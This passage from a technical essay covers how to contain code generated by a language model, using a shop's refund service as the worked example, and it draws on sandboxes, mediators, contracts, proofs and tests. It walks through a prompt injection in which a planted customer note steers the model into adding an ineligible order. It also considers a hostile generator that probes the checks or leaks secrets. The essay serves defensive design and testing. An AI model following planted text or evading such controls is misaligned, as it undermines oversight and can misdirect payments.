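When the attempts run out, the simplest response is to reject the request and tell whoever made it why. This is right when doing nothing is safe, as in the shop, where a late refund is a nuisance but a wrong one costs money. If a check crashes or runs out of time, the service should reject the request then too. Otherwise hostile code could get through by making the type checker run forever.

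Falling back means completing the task another way. The refund service could fall back to the fixed function that takes only dates and a type of refund, which covers the most common requests without generated code. A later step could also hand over to a simpler component that people have verified. TOOLPRO's fallback to separate calls is less secure, because the model reads each result before choosing the next call, and planted text in a result can steer that choice. An attacker who prefers the fallback can also try to trigger it by making the generated program fail. The fallback therefore needs to use the same payment component and limits, and it should get no additional credentials.

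A person can decide cases that no fixed rule covers, but only if the system recognises them. In an example by Trooskens and colleagues, a model extracts values from a patient's chart so that fixed code can decide whether an insurer pays for a drug. The code requests human review if a blood-sugar value is implausible. The specification requires a plausibility check on body mass index, but the printed program has none, even though it approves some patients because their index is at least 30. Unless the extraction step checks the value itself, a misread index of 300 could lead to an approval without human review. The conditions for human review should therefore be in the fixed part of the system, where the model cannot omit them.

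The reviewer at the shop should receive the proposed effects rather than the code. The reviewer can check a list of forty orders, with their delivery dates, promised dates and refunds, in a few minutes and easily spot a parcel that arrived early. The service should hold every payment until the reviewer answers, and treat the request as refused if no answer comes by the end of the day.

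## Checking what the code computes

A reviewer checking a list of forty refunds for late parcels can spot one that arrived early, but can't see from the list that the code left out a late one. To find such omissions, someone has to state what the right result would be. This can be a set of expected answers, rules for a test run, conditions on each result, or a complete formal specification. The more of the code's meaning the statement covers, the harder it usually is to write, and it can also be wrong.

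### Tests with known answers

In *Evaluating the effectiveness of LLM-based interoperability*, Falcão, Schweitzer and colleagues (2025) tested how well models convert data formats at run time. They collected the outlines of 222 real farm fields in GeoJSON, a common map format, and used a script to translate them into a format based on that of the tractor maker John Deere. The original GeoJSON files were therefore the correct answers. A model received the John Deere version of a file and an example of the required GeoJSON. It either converted the file itself or wrote a Python function that the test program ran on the file.

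The easiest version of the task required only the field's outline, the next added the field's identifier, and the third added its area in hectares. The hardest version required the area in acres instead. The test covered twelve open models. For three of them, the table gives the average share of files converted correctly over three runs.

| Model and method | Outline | Outline, identifier | Outline, identifier, hectares | Outline, identifier, acres |
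|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-Coder 32B, direct conversion | 99.7% | 99.5% | 100% | 0% |
| Qwen2.5-Coder 32B, generated code | 89.5% | 91.3% | 93.1% | 75.2% |
| Llama 3 70B, generated code | 90.2% | 93.1% | 89.6% | 1.2% |
| Codestral 22B, generated code | 62.2% | 62.3% | 65.9% | 28.8% |

No model directly converted a single file with acres, probably because that required multiplying long decimal numbers without a calculator. Generated code leaves the multiplication to the computer. But Llama's success rate fell from about 90% to 1% when the task also required one multiplication, so the success rate on one task is a poor guide to the rate on even a very similar task. Falcão and colleagues chose the models in June 2025 and limited them to 70 billion parameters, so current models would probably do better.

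Qwen's code failed in 12.7% of attempts. In 92% of these failures, or nearly 12% of all conversions, the code ran without an error message but returned the wrong data. Comparing the output with the expected answers exposed these errors, which a system that checked only for crashes and compilation errors would have missed.

The expected answers need checking too. All models failed on the first set of files with areas in acres, and Falcão and colleagues found that their own script had converted the areas several times and lost precision. They regenerated the files and repeated the test. But in the example they print, the expected area for a field of 0.0922 hectares is 0.2479 acres, when the correct figure is 0.2277. The error may be only in the printed excerpt, since Qwen's code matched three quarters of the expected files. Someone also has to decide how much rounding error to allow. The comparison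 seems to have allowed very little, so some of the "wrong" areas may have been accurate enough for a farmer to use.

In live use, a service has no expected answer to compare with the output for a new file. *SAGAI-MID* (2026) builds both methods into a layer between systems and adds safeguards against the model's output varying from run to run, but a converter can still make the same mistake every time. A service could instead check that the converted outline has as many corners as the original and that the area in acres is 2.47 times the area in hectares, though such rules catch only the mistakes that someone foresaw.

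### The right number from the wrong analysis

A test that compares only a program's final value can accept a program that computed something other than what was requested. The benchmark in *Knowledge boundary probing and demand-guided intervention for LLM-based power system code generation* contains 2,000 requests for analyses of electricity networks. A program passes if it runs without an error and its final value matches that of a reference program. Suppose the request is to check whether any line is overloaded after a particular line fails. Code that doesn't remove the failed line from the network may answer "no", and it passes if the correct answer is also "no".

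An engineering review checked whether programs that had passed also performed the requested analysis. It confirmed that 66% did when the system returned only error messages for repair, and 88% did when the system also selected relevant documentation for each request and directed repairs at the type of failure. The comparison covers only cases that passed under both arrangements, so better test scores cannot explain the difference. The remaining 34% and 12% gave an acceptable number, but the review did not confirm that they had performed the requested analysis.

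Better test data would expose some of these programs. For the refund code, a test should compare the whole list instead of the total, because different orders can add up to the same amount. The sample table should also contain orders for which the right program and likely wrong ones give different results, such as an order that arrived exactly on the promised day and one that was late in the previous week.

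### Rules for a whole run

For some programs nobody can list the right output for each input, but people can describe what a good run looks like. *Feedback-based Automated Verification in Vibe Coding of CAS Adaptation* (Töpfer, Plášil and colleagues, 2026) tested this with adaptation managers, programs that reassign the parts of a system as conditions change. Its main example is a game invented so that no model could have learned its rules in training. Villagers have 30 turns to kill a dragon, and each turn the manager assigns every villager to one group, such as farming, recruiting warriors or attacking.

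The language model GPT-5 nano wrote the manager in Python, and a fixed program then played the game with it from several starting positions. Some rules apply to any such system. For example, the code must run without an exception and put each villager in exactly one group. Other rules describe the strategy, using this operator:

◇<sup>n</sup><sub>t</sub> φ: condition φ holds in at least n of the next t turns

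The rule "Attack the dragon at least once in the first 15 turns" requires φ, the condition that the attacking group is not empty, to hold on at least n = 1 of the first t = 15 turns. The program counts the turns on which φ holds. The rule succeeds when the count reaches n and fails once φ has been false on more than t − n turns. If a manager breaks a rule, the model receives a report of the violation and writes a new version, up to ten times.

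When the model received detailed reports, it usually produced a manager that satisfied all the rules within a few rounds. Reports that gave only the win rate were less useful. After a report of "win rate is 0%", the model sometimes wrote one manager after another that played the same way. Töpfer and colleagues found that starting over could work better than another repair.

In early trials, several managers obeyed every rule and still lost. One rule required the manager to recruit warriors at least three times. The managers recruited only three, which was too few, and the dragon survived with a few health points. Töpfer and colleagues added the rule about the first 15 turns and a starting position without warriors. After that, every manager that passed the tests also won.

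This last result is less impressive than it sounds, because Töpfer and colleagues had adjusted the rules until the managers that passed also won. The two starting positions they print also fix the random numbers, so a manager that passes from them might lose with less favourable numbers. In a second example, about drones protecting crops from birds, the managers that passed did as well as a hand-written one, with median crop damage of 6.9% against 7.0%. They refined the rules after first trials here too. In both examples, they could tell from the crop damage or lost games which rules were missing. The refund service has no such score, and the shop might never hear from customers who should have received 4.90 euros and did not.

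### Contracts on each result

A run-time contract consists of a precondition, which must hold before the code runs, and a postcondition, which its result must satisfy. The host program checks both on the real data, so it needs no expected answer. For the refund selection, `orders` could hold the shop's own records of the week's deliveries, indexed by order number:

```python
def precondition(orders, start, end):
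    return all(o.promised and o.delivered
               and start <= o.delivered <= end
               for o in orders.values())

def postcondition(orders, refunds):
    ids = [i for i, amount in refunds]
    return len(ids) == len(set(ids)) and all(
        i in orders
        and orders[i].delivered > orders[i].promised
        and amount == min(orders[i].delivery_fee, 50)
        for i, amount in refunds)
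```

The precondition stops the run if a date is missing or an order belongs to another week. The postcondition requires that each refund goes to a different order from the table, that the order came late, and that the amount is right. Suppose the model writes this selection:

```python
late = [o for o in orders if o.delivered >= o.promised]
```

The generated code treats parcels that arrived on the promised day as late. If the week includes even one such parcel, the postcondition fails and the host discards the whole list. The payment component, which checks refunds one at a time, would have rejected the refunds for on-time orders and paid the rest. Discarding the whole list is safer, because code that is wrong about some orders may be wrong about others.

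Now suppose the model writes:

```python
late = [o for o in orders if (o.delivered - o.promised).days > 1]
```

This code leaves out every parcel that came exactly one day late. All the refunds it proposes are correct, so the contract accepts them. To catch the omission, the postcondition would have to compute the full list of late orders itself, which would make the generated code unnecessary.

Complete contracts are useful when a result is easier to check than to find. A few lines of code can check a finished Sudoku, while solving one takes a search. Selecting late orders is as easy as checking the selection, so a complete contract adds little there. Unusual requests, such as one for parcels more than two days late in one region, do need generated code, but a fixed contract does not cover the region or the two days. A model could derive those conditions from the request, but it might repeat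 the same misreading in the code and the conditions, as it might when it writes its own tests.

### Proofs from a producer that nobody trusts

Unlike a contract, which checks one result at a time, a proof can cover every input before the code first runs. *Proof-Carrying Code* (Necula, 1997) showed how a host can rely on a proof without trusting its supplier.

1. The host publishes a safety policy. It contains rules for each operation, such as which memory addresses a program may read, and an interface that states what holds when the code starts and what must hold when it ends.
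2. The producer writes the code and a proof that it obeys the policy.
3. The host derives a formula, the verification condition, from the code and the policy. If the formula is true, the code obeys the policy.
4. A small checker confirms that the supplied proof establishes this formula. The host can then run the code as often as it likes without further checks.

Suppose the code sets `r` to `min(fee, 50)`, the interface promises that `fee` is not negative, and the policy requires `r` to end up between 0 and 50. The host works backwards from the requirement and replaces `r` with the expression that the code assigns to it:

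fee ≥ 0 ⇒ 0 ≤ min(fee, 50) ≤ 50

The proof has two cases. If the fee is at most 50, the minimum is the fee, which lies in the range. Otherwise the minimum is 50. Without the promise about `fee`, the formula would be false for a fee of −10, so it could not be proved. If the code contains a loop, the producer also has to supply an invariant, a condition that holds at the start of every iteration.

Finding a proof can take ingenuity, but checking one is mechanical. If someone changes the code on the way to the host, the host derives a different formula, which the old proof normally doesn't prove. If the old proof does prove it, the changed code also satisfies the policy. The method therefore works even if the generator is hostile. The host has to trust only its policy, the program that derives the formula and the proof checker.

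The policy determines how much of the code's meaning the proof covers. Necula's example is a machine-code function that sums a list of numbers. The proof shows that the function reads only valid memory and that, if it finishes, it returns an integer. A function that always returned 0 would satisfy the same policy. To guarantee the right sum, the host would have to define the sum in its postcondition. The proof also doesn't show that the function finishes, so the host still needs a time limit.

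### When the model writes the proof

*Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking* (Necula and Lee, 1996) calls producing the proofs the main practical difficulty. Language models may make this easier, because a model can try many proofs and a fixed checker rejects the invalid ones.

*Djinnlang* (Henniger, Chong and Amin, 2026) presents a language in which people write only specifications. To specify the maximum of a list, a programmer states that the result is in the list and that no item is larger. A fixed translator turns the specification into obligations for Dafny, a programming language with its own verifier. A language model writes the code and the proofs, and the verifier accepts or rejects them.

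Besides showing that the code meets the specification, the model must prove that some valid result exists for every permitted input and that there is only one. If q(x, o) means that the specification allows output o for input x, the second requirement is:

q(x, o₁) and q(x, o₂) ⇒ o₁ = o₂

If the programmer forgot to state that the maximum is in the list, 10 and 11 would both be acceptable for a list of 3 and 7. The proof would fail, and the programmer would learn that something was missing. The refund contract would fail in the same way, because it accepts both the full list of late orders and an empty one. Requiring every late order to appear would not be enough, since the same refunds could still be listed in a different sequence. The programmer would have to ask for a set or specify the sequence.

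But a specification can be unambiguous and wrong. If the programmer writes ≥ instead of > in the definition of "late", the specification still allows exactly one result, and the model can prove that its code computes that result. For the refund selection, the specification is about as long as the two-line program and about as likely to contain a mistake. The approach is more useful for tasks like sorting, where the specification is much simpler than a fast program.

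Henniger and colleagues also let the model choose how the code works, so a hostile model could write correct code that runs extremely slowly on certain inputs or reveals a secret through its running time. They plan to let programmers specify limits on performance.

In *Djinnlang*, a person writes the specification in advance, but requests to a generate-then-execute system usually arrive in ordinary language. *Towards Formal Verification of LLM-Generated Code from Natural Language Prompts* (Councilman, Fu et al., 2025) proposes a verifier and a formal language that resembles structured ordinary language. Someone still has to read the specification, but this could make it easier for the person who made the request to check.

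In *Trustworthy Software Project Generation*, Fang and Xiong (2026) also automated the specification. They gave an agent the requirements for an interpreter that simulates a simple processor with the 47 instructions of the RISC-V base set. The agent separated pure calculation from input and output, then wrote functions, properties and proofs for the calculations in Rocq. An extraction tool translated the accepted functions into C++, and the agent wrote the remaining C++ itself. The work took under 30 minutes with Claude Opus 4.7 and produced 1,859 lines of Rocq and 2,848 lines of extracted C++.

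For example, for an instruction that jumps to a computed address, the agent proved that the return address goes into the right register, that the jump goes to the right place, and that memory and all other registers stay the same. The last property is easy to forget, but without it an instruction could compute the right values and still corrupt an unrelated register.

The interpreter passed 265 tests and ran 98.2 million random inputs in twelve hours without crashing or hanging. The work shows that a model can now complete a substantial proof without help. It is weaker evidence that the interpreter is correct, because a model wrote both the tests and the properties, and the random runs could reveal only crashes and hangs. If the agent misread the processor manual, it could have proved that its code meets properties that describe the wrong behaviour. A comparison with an independently written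 RISC-V simulator would be more convincing.

A run with Dafny did not finish in the same 30 minutes. Fang and Xiong attribute this to Rocq's feedback, which shows the model exactly what remains to be proved when an attempt fails, while Dafny's solver often just ran out of time. With one reported run for each, this is only a plausible explanation.

### What lies outside the proof

A proof connects a piece of code to a specification under a model of the machine and everything else around the code. An error in the specification, in that model or in the translation from the proved code to the running program can make a valid proof irrelevant. The three systems leave different parts to trust:

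| System | Who specifies the result | What the proof covers | What remains to trust |
|---|---|---|---|
| Necula | The host's designer | The machine instructions themselves | The formula generator, the checker and the model of the processor |
| Henniger and colleagues | The programmer | Dafny code | The translator, the Dafny verifier and the Dafny compiler |
| Fang and Xiong | A model, from written requirements | Functions in Rocq | Rocq, the extraction tool, the C++ compiler and the unverified C++ around the functions |

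Hu and colleagues prefer to check effects at run time partly because of these gaps. A supporter of proofs can reply that the gaps can be avoided. If people verify the compiler, the operating system and every other layer down to a trusted model of the machine, a proof about the source code carries over to the instructions that run. A mediator would then only repeat checks that can never fail. Foundational proof-carrying code, described in an abstract in the *PCC Reading List*, works towards this by minimising the axioms, the verifier and the runtime system.

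The reply is correct for properties that depend only on the program and the machine, though somebody still has to specify the right property and the hardware has to match its model. It is less persuasive for the refund service, because whether another 50 euros would exceed the day's limit depends on payments from earlier runs. Something has to keep the running total between runs and protect it from the next program, which is already most of what a mediator does. The payment provider and the delivery records are also outside any model of the machine. However, a proof could show that the payment component applies its limits correctly. This code is short and rarely changes, so the proof would seldom need redoing.

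### Falling back on a simpler program

The Simplex architecture pairs a complex program that nobody can verify with a simpler, verified one that is ready to take over. Lui Sha described it in a 2001 article. Crenshaw (2008) explains it as a way to combine two algorithms to get the safety of one and the features of the other.

Sha's *Integrate Mixed-Criticality Components with Formalized Architectural Patterns* illustrates the idea with sorting. A fast sorting program is too complex to verify, but bubble sort, which is slower, has been proved correct. The fast program may rearrange the items only through a verified component that cannot add, change or delete any. If the fast program finishes on time, a fixed program checks in one pass that the output is in order. If the check fails or time runs out, bubble sort sorts the items. The result is always correct, regardless of who or what wrote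 the fast program.

A machine's controller is harder to check, because there may be no way to tell whether a command is the best one. Simplex therefore checks where the command would lead. If the machine could reach a state from which the simple controller could not recover, the monitor rejects the command. Otherwise it lets the complex controller continue. Sha's real-world example is the Boeing 777, which has a new, complex normal flight controller and a secondary controller based on the control laws of the older 747. The aircraft should stay within the range of states that the secondary controller can keep stable.

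Suppose generated code drives a warehouse cart towards a wall at 4 metres per second. A verified controller can brake at 2 metres per second squared, so from this speed it needs 4²/(2 × 2) = 4 metres to stop. But the monitor checks only every 0.1 seconds, and the generated code might accelerate by 2 metres per second squared until the next check. The cart would then travel 0.41 metres and reach 4.2 metres per second, from which it needs 4.41 metres to stop. The monitor therefore has to switch to the verified controller if the cart is less than 4.82 metres from the wall.

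For the architecture to work, the designer must know the safe region, which here means all combinations of speed and distance from which the brakes can still prevent a crash. The monitor must measure both values correctly, and the switch must happen before the cart leaves the region. If worn brakes produce only half the assumed deceleration, the calculated region is wrong and the cart hits the wall even though the software works as designed. The rule about attacking the dragon within 15 turns would make a poor monitor, because it fails only after half the game is over.

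Sha adds that faults in the complex program must not be able to corrupt the simple program or the software that switches between them. If a model writes the complex program, it must run in a sandbox. The simple program also needs guaranteed processor time, because generated code could otherwise delay the braking by keeping the processor busy.

The refund service's fallback to its fixed function resembles the sorting example, because the generated code returns its list before any money moves. But the contract accepts lists with missing orders, so an omission would never trigger the fallback. Unusual requests also have no verified program to fall back to. Simplex is most useful when the generated code does the same job as the verified code, but faster or better, as in sorting and flight control.

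## A complete design worked through, and how to test it

Suppose a staff member asks the refund service to "refund the delivery fee on everything that came more than two days late" in the week from 28 September to 4 October. That week 40 parcels came late, 12 of them by more than two days and 9 by exactly two. Each customer had paid a delivery fee of 4.90 euros, so the right result is 12 refunds, or 58.80 euros.

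### From request to payment

1. Request: the member of staff types the request and enters the first and last delivery date in separate fields.
2. Prompt: a fixed program sends the model the request, the permitted syntax, and the names and types of four order fields (number, promised date, delivery date and fee). It sends no customer messages and no rows from the table.
3. Code: the model may write one function, which takes the week's orders and returns order numbers. It no longer returns amounts, because the mediator calculates them from the order records. An amount from the code could only be redundant, wrong or a hidden signal.
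4. Execution gate: a parser and a syntax allow-list check the code, then a type checker, each with a time limit. The gate records a hash of the text that passed.
5. Sandbox: the host starts a new virtual machine with the strict settings described earlier, confirms the hash, runs the code, reads the list and destroys the machine.
6. List check: a fixed program compares every order on the list with the shop's records and rejects the whole list if one order is ineligible.
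7. Approval: a list worth more than 250 euros waits for the member of staff to approve it.
8. Payment: the mediator checks each refund again and pays it.

If the code fails at the gate or in the sandbox, the model gets up to two more attempts, and each new program starts at the parser. The model sees the type checker's messages in full, because the type checker never handles order data. It sees only the error type and line number for failures in the sandbox. If a list fails the list check, the request ends, because explaining the failure would help a steered or hostile model find a list that passes.

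An approval applies only to the exact list, which the mediator identifies by its hash. Otherwise, an agent with permission to take a test machine out of service could use that permission on a production database, as *KedgeFlow* (He and Yu, 2026) describes.

The mediator knows only one operation and refuses everything else:

```
operation REFUND
permit    order delivered between the two dates
          order delivered after its promised date
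          order has no earlier refund, paid or unknown
          amount = min(delivery_fee, 50) and amount > 0
          paid_today + amount <= 2000
outcome   paid, refused, unknown
```

The mediator handles one refund at a time and derives each payment's unique number from the order number, so it cannot refund the same order twice, even if two approved requests overlap. The gateway in He and Yu's design treats two separate permissions for the same action as unrelated, so they leave this problem to whoever issues the permissions. If the payment provider sends a response outside the three listed outcomes, the mediator stops paying until a person has investigated, as Hu and colleagues recommend.

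For each request, the log contains the request and its dates, the model's version, every program it wrote, the result of each check, the orders that went into the sandbox, the list that came out, and every payment with the provider's response. The mediator writes an entry before it sends a payment and another when the response arrives. Only fixed components can add entries, and they can't change existing ones. The shop can therefore rerun any program later on the same data.

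### Three programs

The first program contains a type error:

```python
def select(orders: list[Order]) -> list[OrderId]:
    return [o.id for o in orders if o.delivered - o.promised > 2]
```

Subtracting two dates gives a time span, which Python cannot compare with the number 2, so the type checker rejects the program before it runs. The model receives the error message and writes `(o.delivered - o.promised).days > 2`, which passes every check and selects the right 12 orders.

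For the second program, suppose the member of staff pastes a customer's note into the request as an example of the complaints. The note contains the planted sentence about a 900-euro refund for order 1182, so it reaches the model even though the service keeps messages out of the prompt. The model writes:

```python
def select(orders: list[Order]) -> list[OrderId]:
    return [o.id for o in orders
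            if (o.delivered - o.promised).days > 2 or o.id == 1182]
```

The syntax and types are correct, and the sandbox returns 13 order numbers. The program cannot request 900 euros. The parcel for order 1182 came early, so the list check rejects the whole list, and the member of staff learns which order caused the rejection. No refunds are issued yet, even to the 12 customers who should receive one. If the parcel for order 1182 had come one day late, the list would have passed the check and that customer would have received 4.90 euros.

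The third program reads "more than two days" as "two days or more":

```python
def select(orders: list[Order]) -> list[OrderId]:
    return [o.id for o in orders if (o.delivered - o.promised).days >= 2]
```

The program selects 21 orders worth 102.90 euros. All came late in the right week, and the total is below the approval threshold, so the service pays them. Nine customers receive a total of 44.10 euros that the request did not cover. Nothing stops this program, because the two-day condition appears only in the typed request and no fixed component can interpret it.

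*Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* places such cases outside its guarantee because the policy permits the action. He and Yu deliberately produced such a case, in which their gateway authorised a harmful change under a policy that was too permissive. A form field for the minimum delay would let the mediator refuse the nine refunds, but the next unusual request would need another field.

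The fixed rules still limit the damage a hostile program can do. It can refuse to pay anybody, but it can pay only customers whose parcels came late that week, and only their recorded fees. The request covers 12 of these 40 customers, so the program can misdirect at most 28 refunds, or 137.20 euros.

### What each guarantee depends on

| Guarantee | Component that provides it | Assumption that would void it if false |
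|---|---|---|
| Only code with permitted syntax and correct types runs. | Execution gate | The checkers have no exploitable bug, and no other component runs generated text. |
| The code reads only the supplied orders and software, and stops within ten seconds. | Sandbox | The monitor, the host's kernel and the processor isolate the virtual machine, and the host applies every limit before it loads the code. |
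| Every payment passes the mediator's check. | Component graph | No other component has the payment password or another way to move money. |
| No order receives more than 50 euros, and the service pays at most 2,000 euros a day. | Mediator | It handles one refund at a time, its clock is right, and nobody restores its totals from an old backup. |
| Only orders that came late in the chosen week receive refunds, at the recorded fee. | Mediator | The order records are right, and the generated code cannot change them. |
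| No order receives two refunds. | Mediator and payment provider | The provider recognises a repeated payment number. |
| Customer messages do not influence the code. | The program that builds the prompt | Nobody pastes a message into the request. |
| The log contains every payment and the program behind it. | Mediator and host | No component can delete or change an entry. |
| The service refunds the orders that the request meant. | None | – |

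The second program broke the assumption about pasted messages, but the guarantee about late orders still held because it doesn't depend on the prompt. For the last row, the shop can only measure how often the service is right.

*Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* also excludes policies that let an agent change the policy or the monitor's state. So no permitted request in the shop may raise the daily limit or edit the order records.

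### Replacing the model with a script

Most of these guarantees hold for any program, so an assessor can test them by replacing the language model with a scripted generator, a function that ignores the prompt and returns a program the assessor has chosen. The script takes little compute, and its results are repeatable. It can also produce attacks that a well-behaved model might refuse to write or might write only once in a million attempts. If a supposed guarantee fails with the script, it held only because of how the model usually behaves.

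In *Containment Verification*, Moon and Varshney (2026) use the same substitution in a proof, replacing the model with a procedure that has no body and may return any action of the right type. For PocketFlow, a small framework for building agents, they prove that every such action leads only to effects their policy permits, provided that no effect bypasses the framework. They call this a universal guarantee, as opposed to an empirical one, which covers only the inputs somebody tried. Tests with a script are still empirical, but a single failure refutes a universal claim.

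He and Yu used a scripted component that always emits the redirected request, so their results concern the gateway rather than how easily an attack can redirect a model. They also had 32 or 128 clients compete simultaneously for single-use permissions. In 6,560 attempts on 82 permissions, each permission worked exactly once. This is good evidence that the locking works, but all the tests ran on one computer, the protected system was a mock, and they did not test crashes at each stage.

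For the refund service, the assessor could submit 32 simultaneous requests for the same order and count the payments. If the service has already paid 1,960 euros that day, two simultaneous requests for 40-euro refunds should result in only one payment.

A model can also help write attacks. In *Attested Tool-Server Admission* (2026), which proposes a way to check the servers that provide tools to agents, a local model produced 14,378 distinct forged clearances, and the gate rejected them all. These attempts mostly repeat one test, because a valid clearance needs a digital signature and the model did not have the key. The missing key is a better reason for confidence than the gate being deterministic, which is why the paper claims full coverage. A deterministic gate always gives the same answer to the same input, but it could still wrongly accept an input that nobody tried.

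### A negative test for each forbidden effect

A negative test attempts a forbidden action and passes only if the action doesn't happen. The assessor should look for evidence outside the component under test, because a faulty mediator might report a refusal and make the payment anyway. The sandbox tests below bypass the gate, which would otherwise reject most of the test programs before they reached the sandbox.

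| Forbidden effect | Test | Evidence of a pass |
|---|---|---|
| Refund for a parcel that was on time | Return an order delivered on the promised day | No payment in the provider's test account |
| Payments above the daily limit | With 1,960 euros paid, request refunds for orders with fees of 40 and 0.01 euros, in that order | Only the payment of 40 euros |
| Sending data out | Open a connection, then look up a name that the assessor's own server handles | No packet and no query outside the sandbox |
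| Leaving something for the next run | Write a file and look for it in the next run | The file is missing |
| Running too long | Sleep for a minute | The host destroys the machine after ten seconds and pays nothing |
| Running unchecked text | Change one character after the gate | The host refuses to run the program |

Tests should include the exact limit. AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies* gives an example in which refunds may be "$500 or less", but its policy requires `amount < 500`. A test in AWS's *policy integration* requests a refund of $750, which such a policy correctly refuses. Only a test with exactly $500 reveals the mismatch. This mistake blocks a legitimate refund, but the opposite mistake would allow a forbidden one. The condition also accepts negative amounts, and because it limits only single refunds, it would allow any number of $499 refunds. The sample test prints the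 response next to the comment "Should DENY" and leaves the reader to compare them, but an automatic test should make that comparison and fail if they differ.

Random testing would probably miss this kind of mistake. A random amount between 0.01 and 2,000.00 euros is exactly 2,000.00 only once in 200,000 draws on average.

The tests should come from the list of forbidden effects, not from the checker's own rules. *A Deterministic Control Plane for LLM Coding Agents* (2026) tested its checks by altering files after recording their checksums, giving read-only agents forbidden tools, and constructing shell commands that match its list of forbidden patterns. These commands confirm that the patterns work, but they cannot reveal a harmful command that no pattern matches. The paper rightly calls its tests conformance testing and makes no claim about effectiveness in use.

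Each negative test also needs a matching case that the mediator should permit, such as an order that came one day late, because a mediator that refuses everything would pass all the negative tests.

### Looking for a way around the mediator

The assessor can search the component graph automatically for paths to payments that avoid the mediator, but this search covers only the connections in the diagram. An inventory should also include the others that He and Yu list: direct programming interfaces, shell credentials, remote sessions, subagents, administrative clients and inherited tokens. The assessor should therefore build the graph from the running system, including its network rules, accounts and scheduled jobs.

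One practical test is to change the payment password and give the new one only to the mediator. Anything else that stops working had a copy of the old password. The assessor should also compare the provider's account statement with the mediator's log. Any payment that appears only in the statement bypassed the mediator.

### Removing one layer at a time

A successful test of the whole service shows only that at least one layer worked. The allow-list may reject every attack and hide a sandbox that was never switched on. On a test copy, the assessor can disable one layer at a time:

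| Disabled layer | Test program | What still holds | What is lost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Type checker | Compares a time span with a number | The program crashes in the sandbox and returns no list. | The full error message for the repair |
| Syntax allow-list | Opens the orders database for writing | The virtual machine does not contain the database. | The barrier in front of the sandbox |
| Sandbox | Builds a list of 100 million orders | No payment happens, because the process has no password. | The memory limit, so the host may crash |
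| List check | Adds order 1182 | The mediator refuses order 1182. | The other 12 refunds go out, although the program was steered. |
| Mediator's comparison with the records | Adds order 1182 | The list check rejects the list. | Protection if a record changes before payment |

This kind of test would have separated the samples that *STELP*'s rules blocked from the deadlocks and endless loops that only the time limit stopped.

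The list check and the mediator both use the shop's order records, so they are not independent. If the assessor enters a false delivery date for order 1182, both accept the refund. Comparing the date with the carrier's own records would be a more independent check. Multiplying the miss rates of two layers is unreliable for the same reason. Two filters that each miss 1% of attacks let through 1 in 10,000 if their misses are independent, but 1 in 100 if they miss the same ones.

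### What a clean result supports

Suppose a filter blocks all 470 unsafe samples in a test, as *STELP* did. If its true miss rate is p, the probability of this result is (1 − p)<sup>470</sup>. Setting this equal to 5% gives:

p = 1 − 0.05<sup>1/470</sup> ≈ 0.64%

The upper 95% confidence bound on the miss rate is 0.64%, because at any higher rate the test would have had more than a 95% chance of finding at least one miss. When a test finds no misses, this bound is approximately 3 divided by the number of samples. To lower it to 1 in 10,000, the test would need about 30,000 samples without a miss.

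The bound assumes the samples are independent draws from the same source as future programs. The 470 samples cover 12 kinds of weakness, with 32 to 50 samples of each. For the kind with 32 samples, the bound is 8.9%. The samples may not be independent, because they are variants of at most 164 original programs. If all variants of a program passed or failed together, there would be at most 164 independent results and the bound would be at least 1.8%. The bound also covers only weaknesses like those one language model inserted, so it does not apply to a hostile generator.

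Scripted tests also don't measure how useful the service is with a real model. In *If Agents Were Angels, No Governance Would Be Necessary*, Millstone, Akidau and colleagues (2026) therefore report conformance tests and model trials separately. They put a policy check between agents and two simulated business systems and ran 3,621 trials with four models. A trial failed if protected data reached the agent, an exact protected value appeared in its answer, or a forbidden change happened. In the main comparison, the failure rate fell from 57.6% to 0.2%, but the share of tasks completed also fell, from 79.1% to 60.9%.

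Among the remaining failures, four answers contained a protected value that the agent had reconstructed without ever receiving it. In another trial, the agent inferred protected information from the number of rows that a filtered search returned. A negative test that only checks whether a field is missing would not detect either kind of leak.

For the refund service, the shop could collect 200 past requests with known correct lists and run them through the service with the real model. If 6 of the resulting lists are wrong, the measured error rate is 3%, with a 95% confidence interval of about 1% to 6%. The third program would count as an error even though every guarantee held.

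### What a short trial misses

Some faults appear only after hours of operation. In *Software Aging in LLM-Generated Applications*, Santos, Vitagliano and colleagues (2026) had language models write four web services, each in JavaScript, Python and Rust. All 12 programs passed functional tests and then handled requests for 48 hours. Memory use rose significantly in 11 of the 12 runs, by up to 4.4 MB an hour. At the highest rate, memory use would grow by less than 1 MB in a ten-minute test, but it grew by about 210 MB over the two days and would grow by more than 3 GB in a month. In some runs, the service also became slower or handled fewer requests per second.

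A review of the code found likely causes. Some programs kept adding records without deleting any, and one left temporary files behind when an image conversion failed. These explanations are tentative because Santos and colleagues measured the memory of the whole server, so part of the growth may have come from other software. The test also repeated a fixed set of requests, which may have kept some tables from growing as they would in real use. *Investigating Software Aging in LLM-Generated Software Systems* (2025), an earlier study by the same group, also found signs of degradation in all four of its generated applications.

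The generated refund code cannot age like this, because its virtual machine lasts at most ten seconds. But the host program and the mediator run for months, and hand-written code ages too. Santos and colleagues made three comparisons with human-written Python programs, and memory grew faster in the human-written version in all three.

The scripted generator makes a long trial practical. If staff make 30 requests a day, it can send a year's worth, 10,950 requests, in about 30 hours at one every ten seconds. The requests should vary and include failures, since any leftover virtual machines and files are likely to come from the cleanup after a failed run. The assessor should also move the test clock past midnight and through the change to winter time, because the daily limit depends on the clock.

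### When to test again

A new model changes the measured rates, such as how often the list is right, how many repairs a request needs and how often a request ends without a result. The shop should repeat the 200 requests after every change of model or prompt. The guarantees don't depend on the model, so the payment tests remain valid. But a more capable model may find a flaw in the sandbox that earlier models missed, so the shop should also review the evidence for its assumption that the sandbox is secure.

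A change to a checker, the mediator's policy, the sandbox or the component graph can void a guarantee. After any such change, the shop should repeat the scripted tests, the negative tests, the graph search and the removal of layers. The same applies to less obvious changes, such as a new Python version with additional syntax, a new column in the orders table, another service with access to the payment provider, or a change in the provider's responses. The shop should also act when a new flaw in the virtual machine monitor is published, even if nothing in its own system has changed.

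When the policy changes, a proof can cover more cases than tests can. *Tether* (2026) presents a policy system for agents in which a user states what must never happen, and a language model tries to prove that the policy prevents it for every sequence of actions, however long. The proof assistant Lean then checks the proof.

The proof for the daily limit is short. The total starts each day at zero, and the policy permits a refund only if the new total is at most 2,000 euros, so the total stays within the limit after any number of refunds. If someone later changes the rule to test `paid_today <= 2000` without adding the new amount, the proof fails, because a refund of 50 euros could raise the total from 2,000 to 2,050. The proof covers only the written policy, so the shop still has to test the program that applies it.
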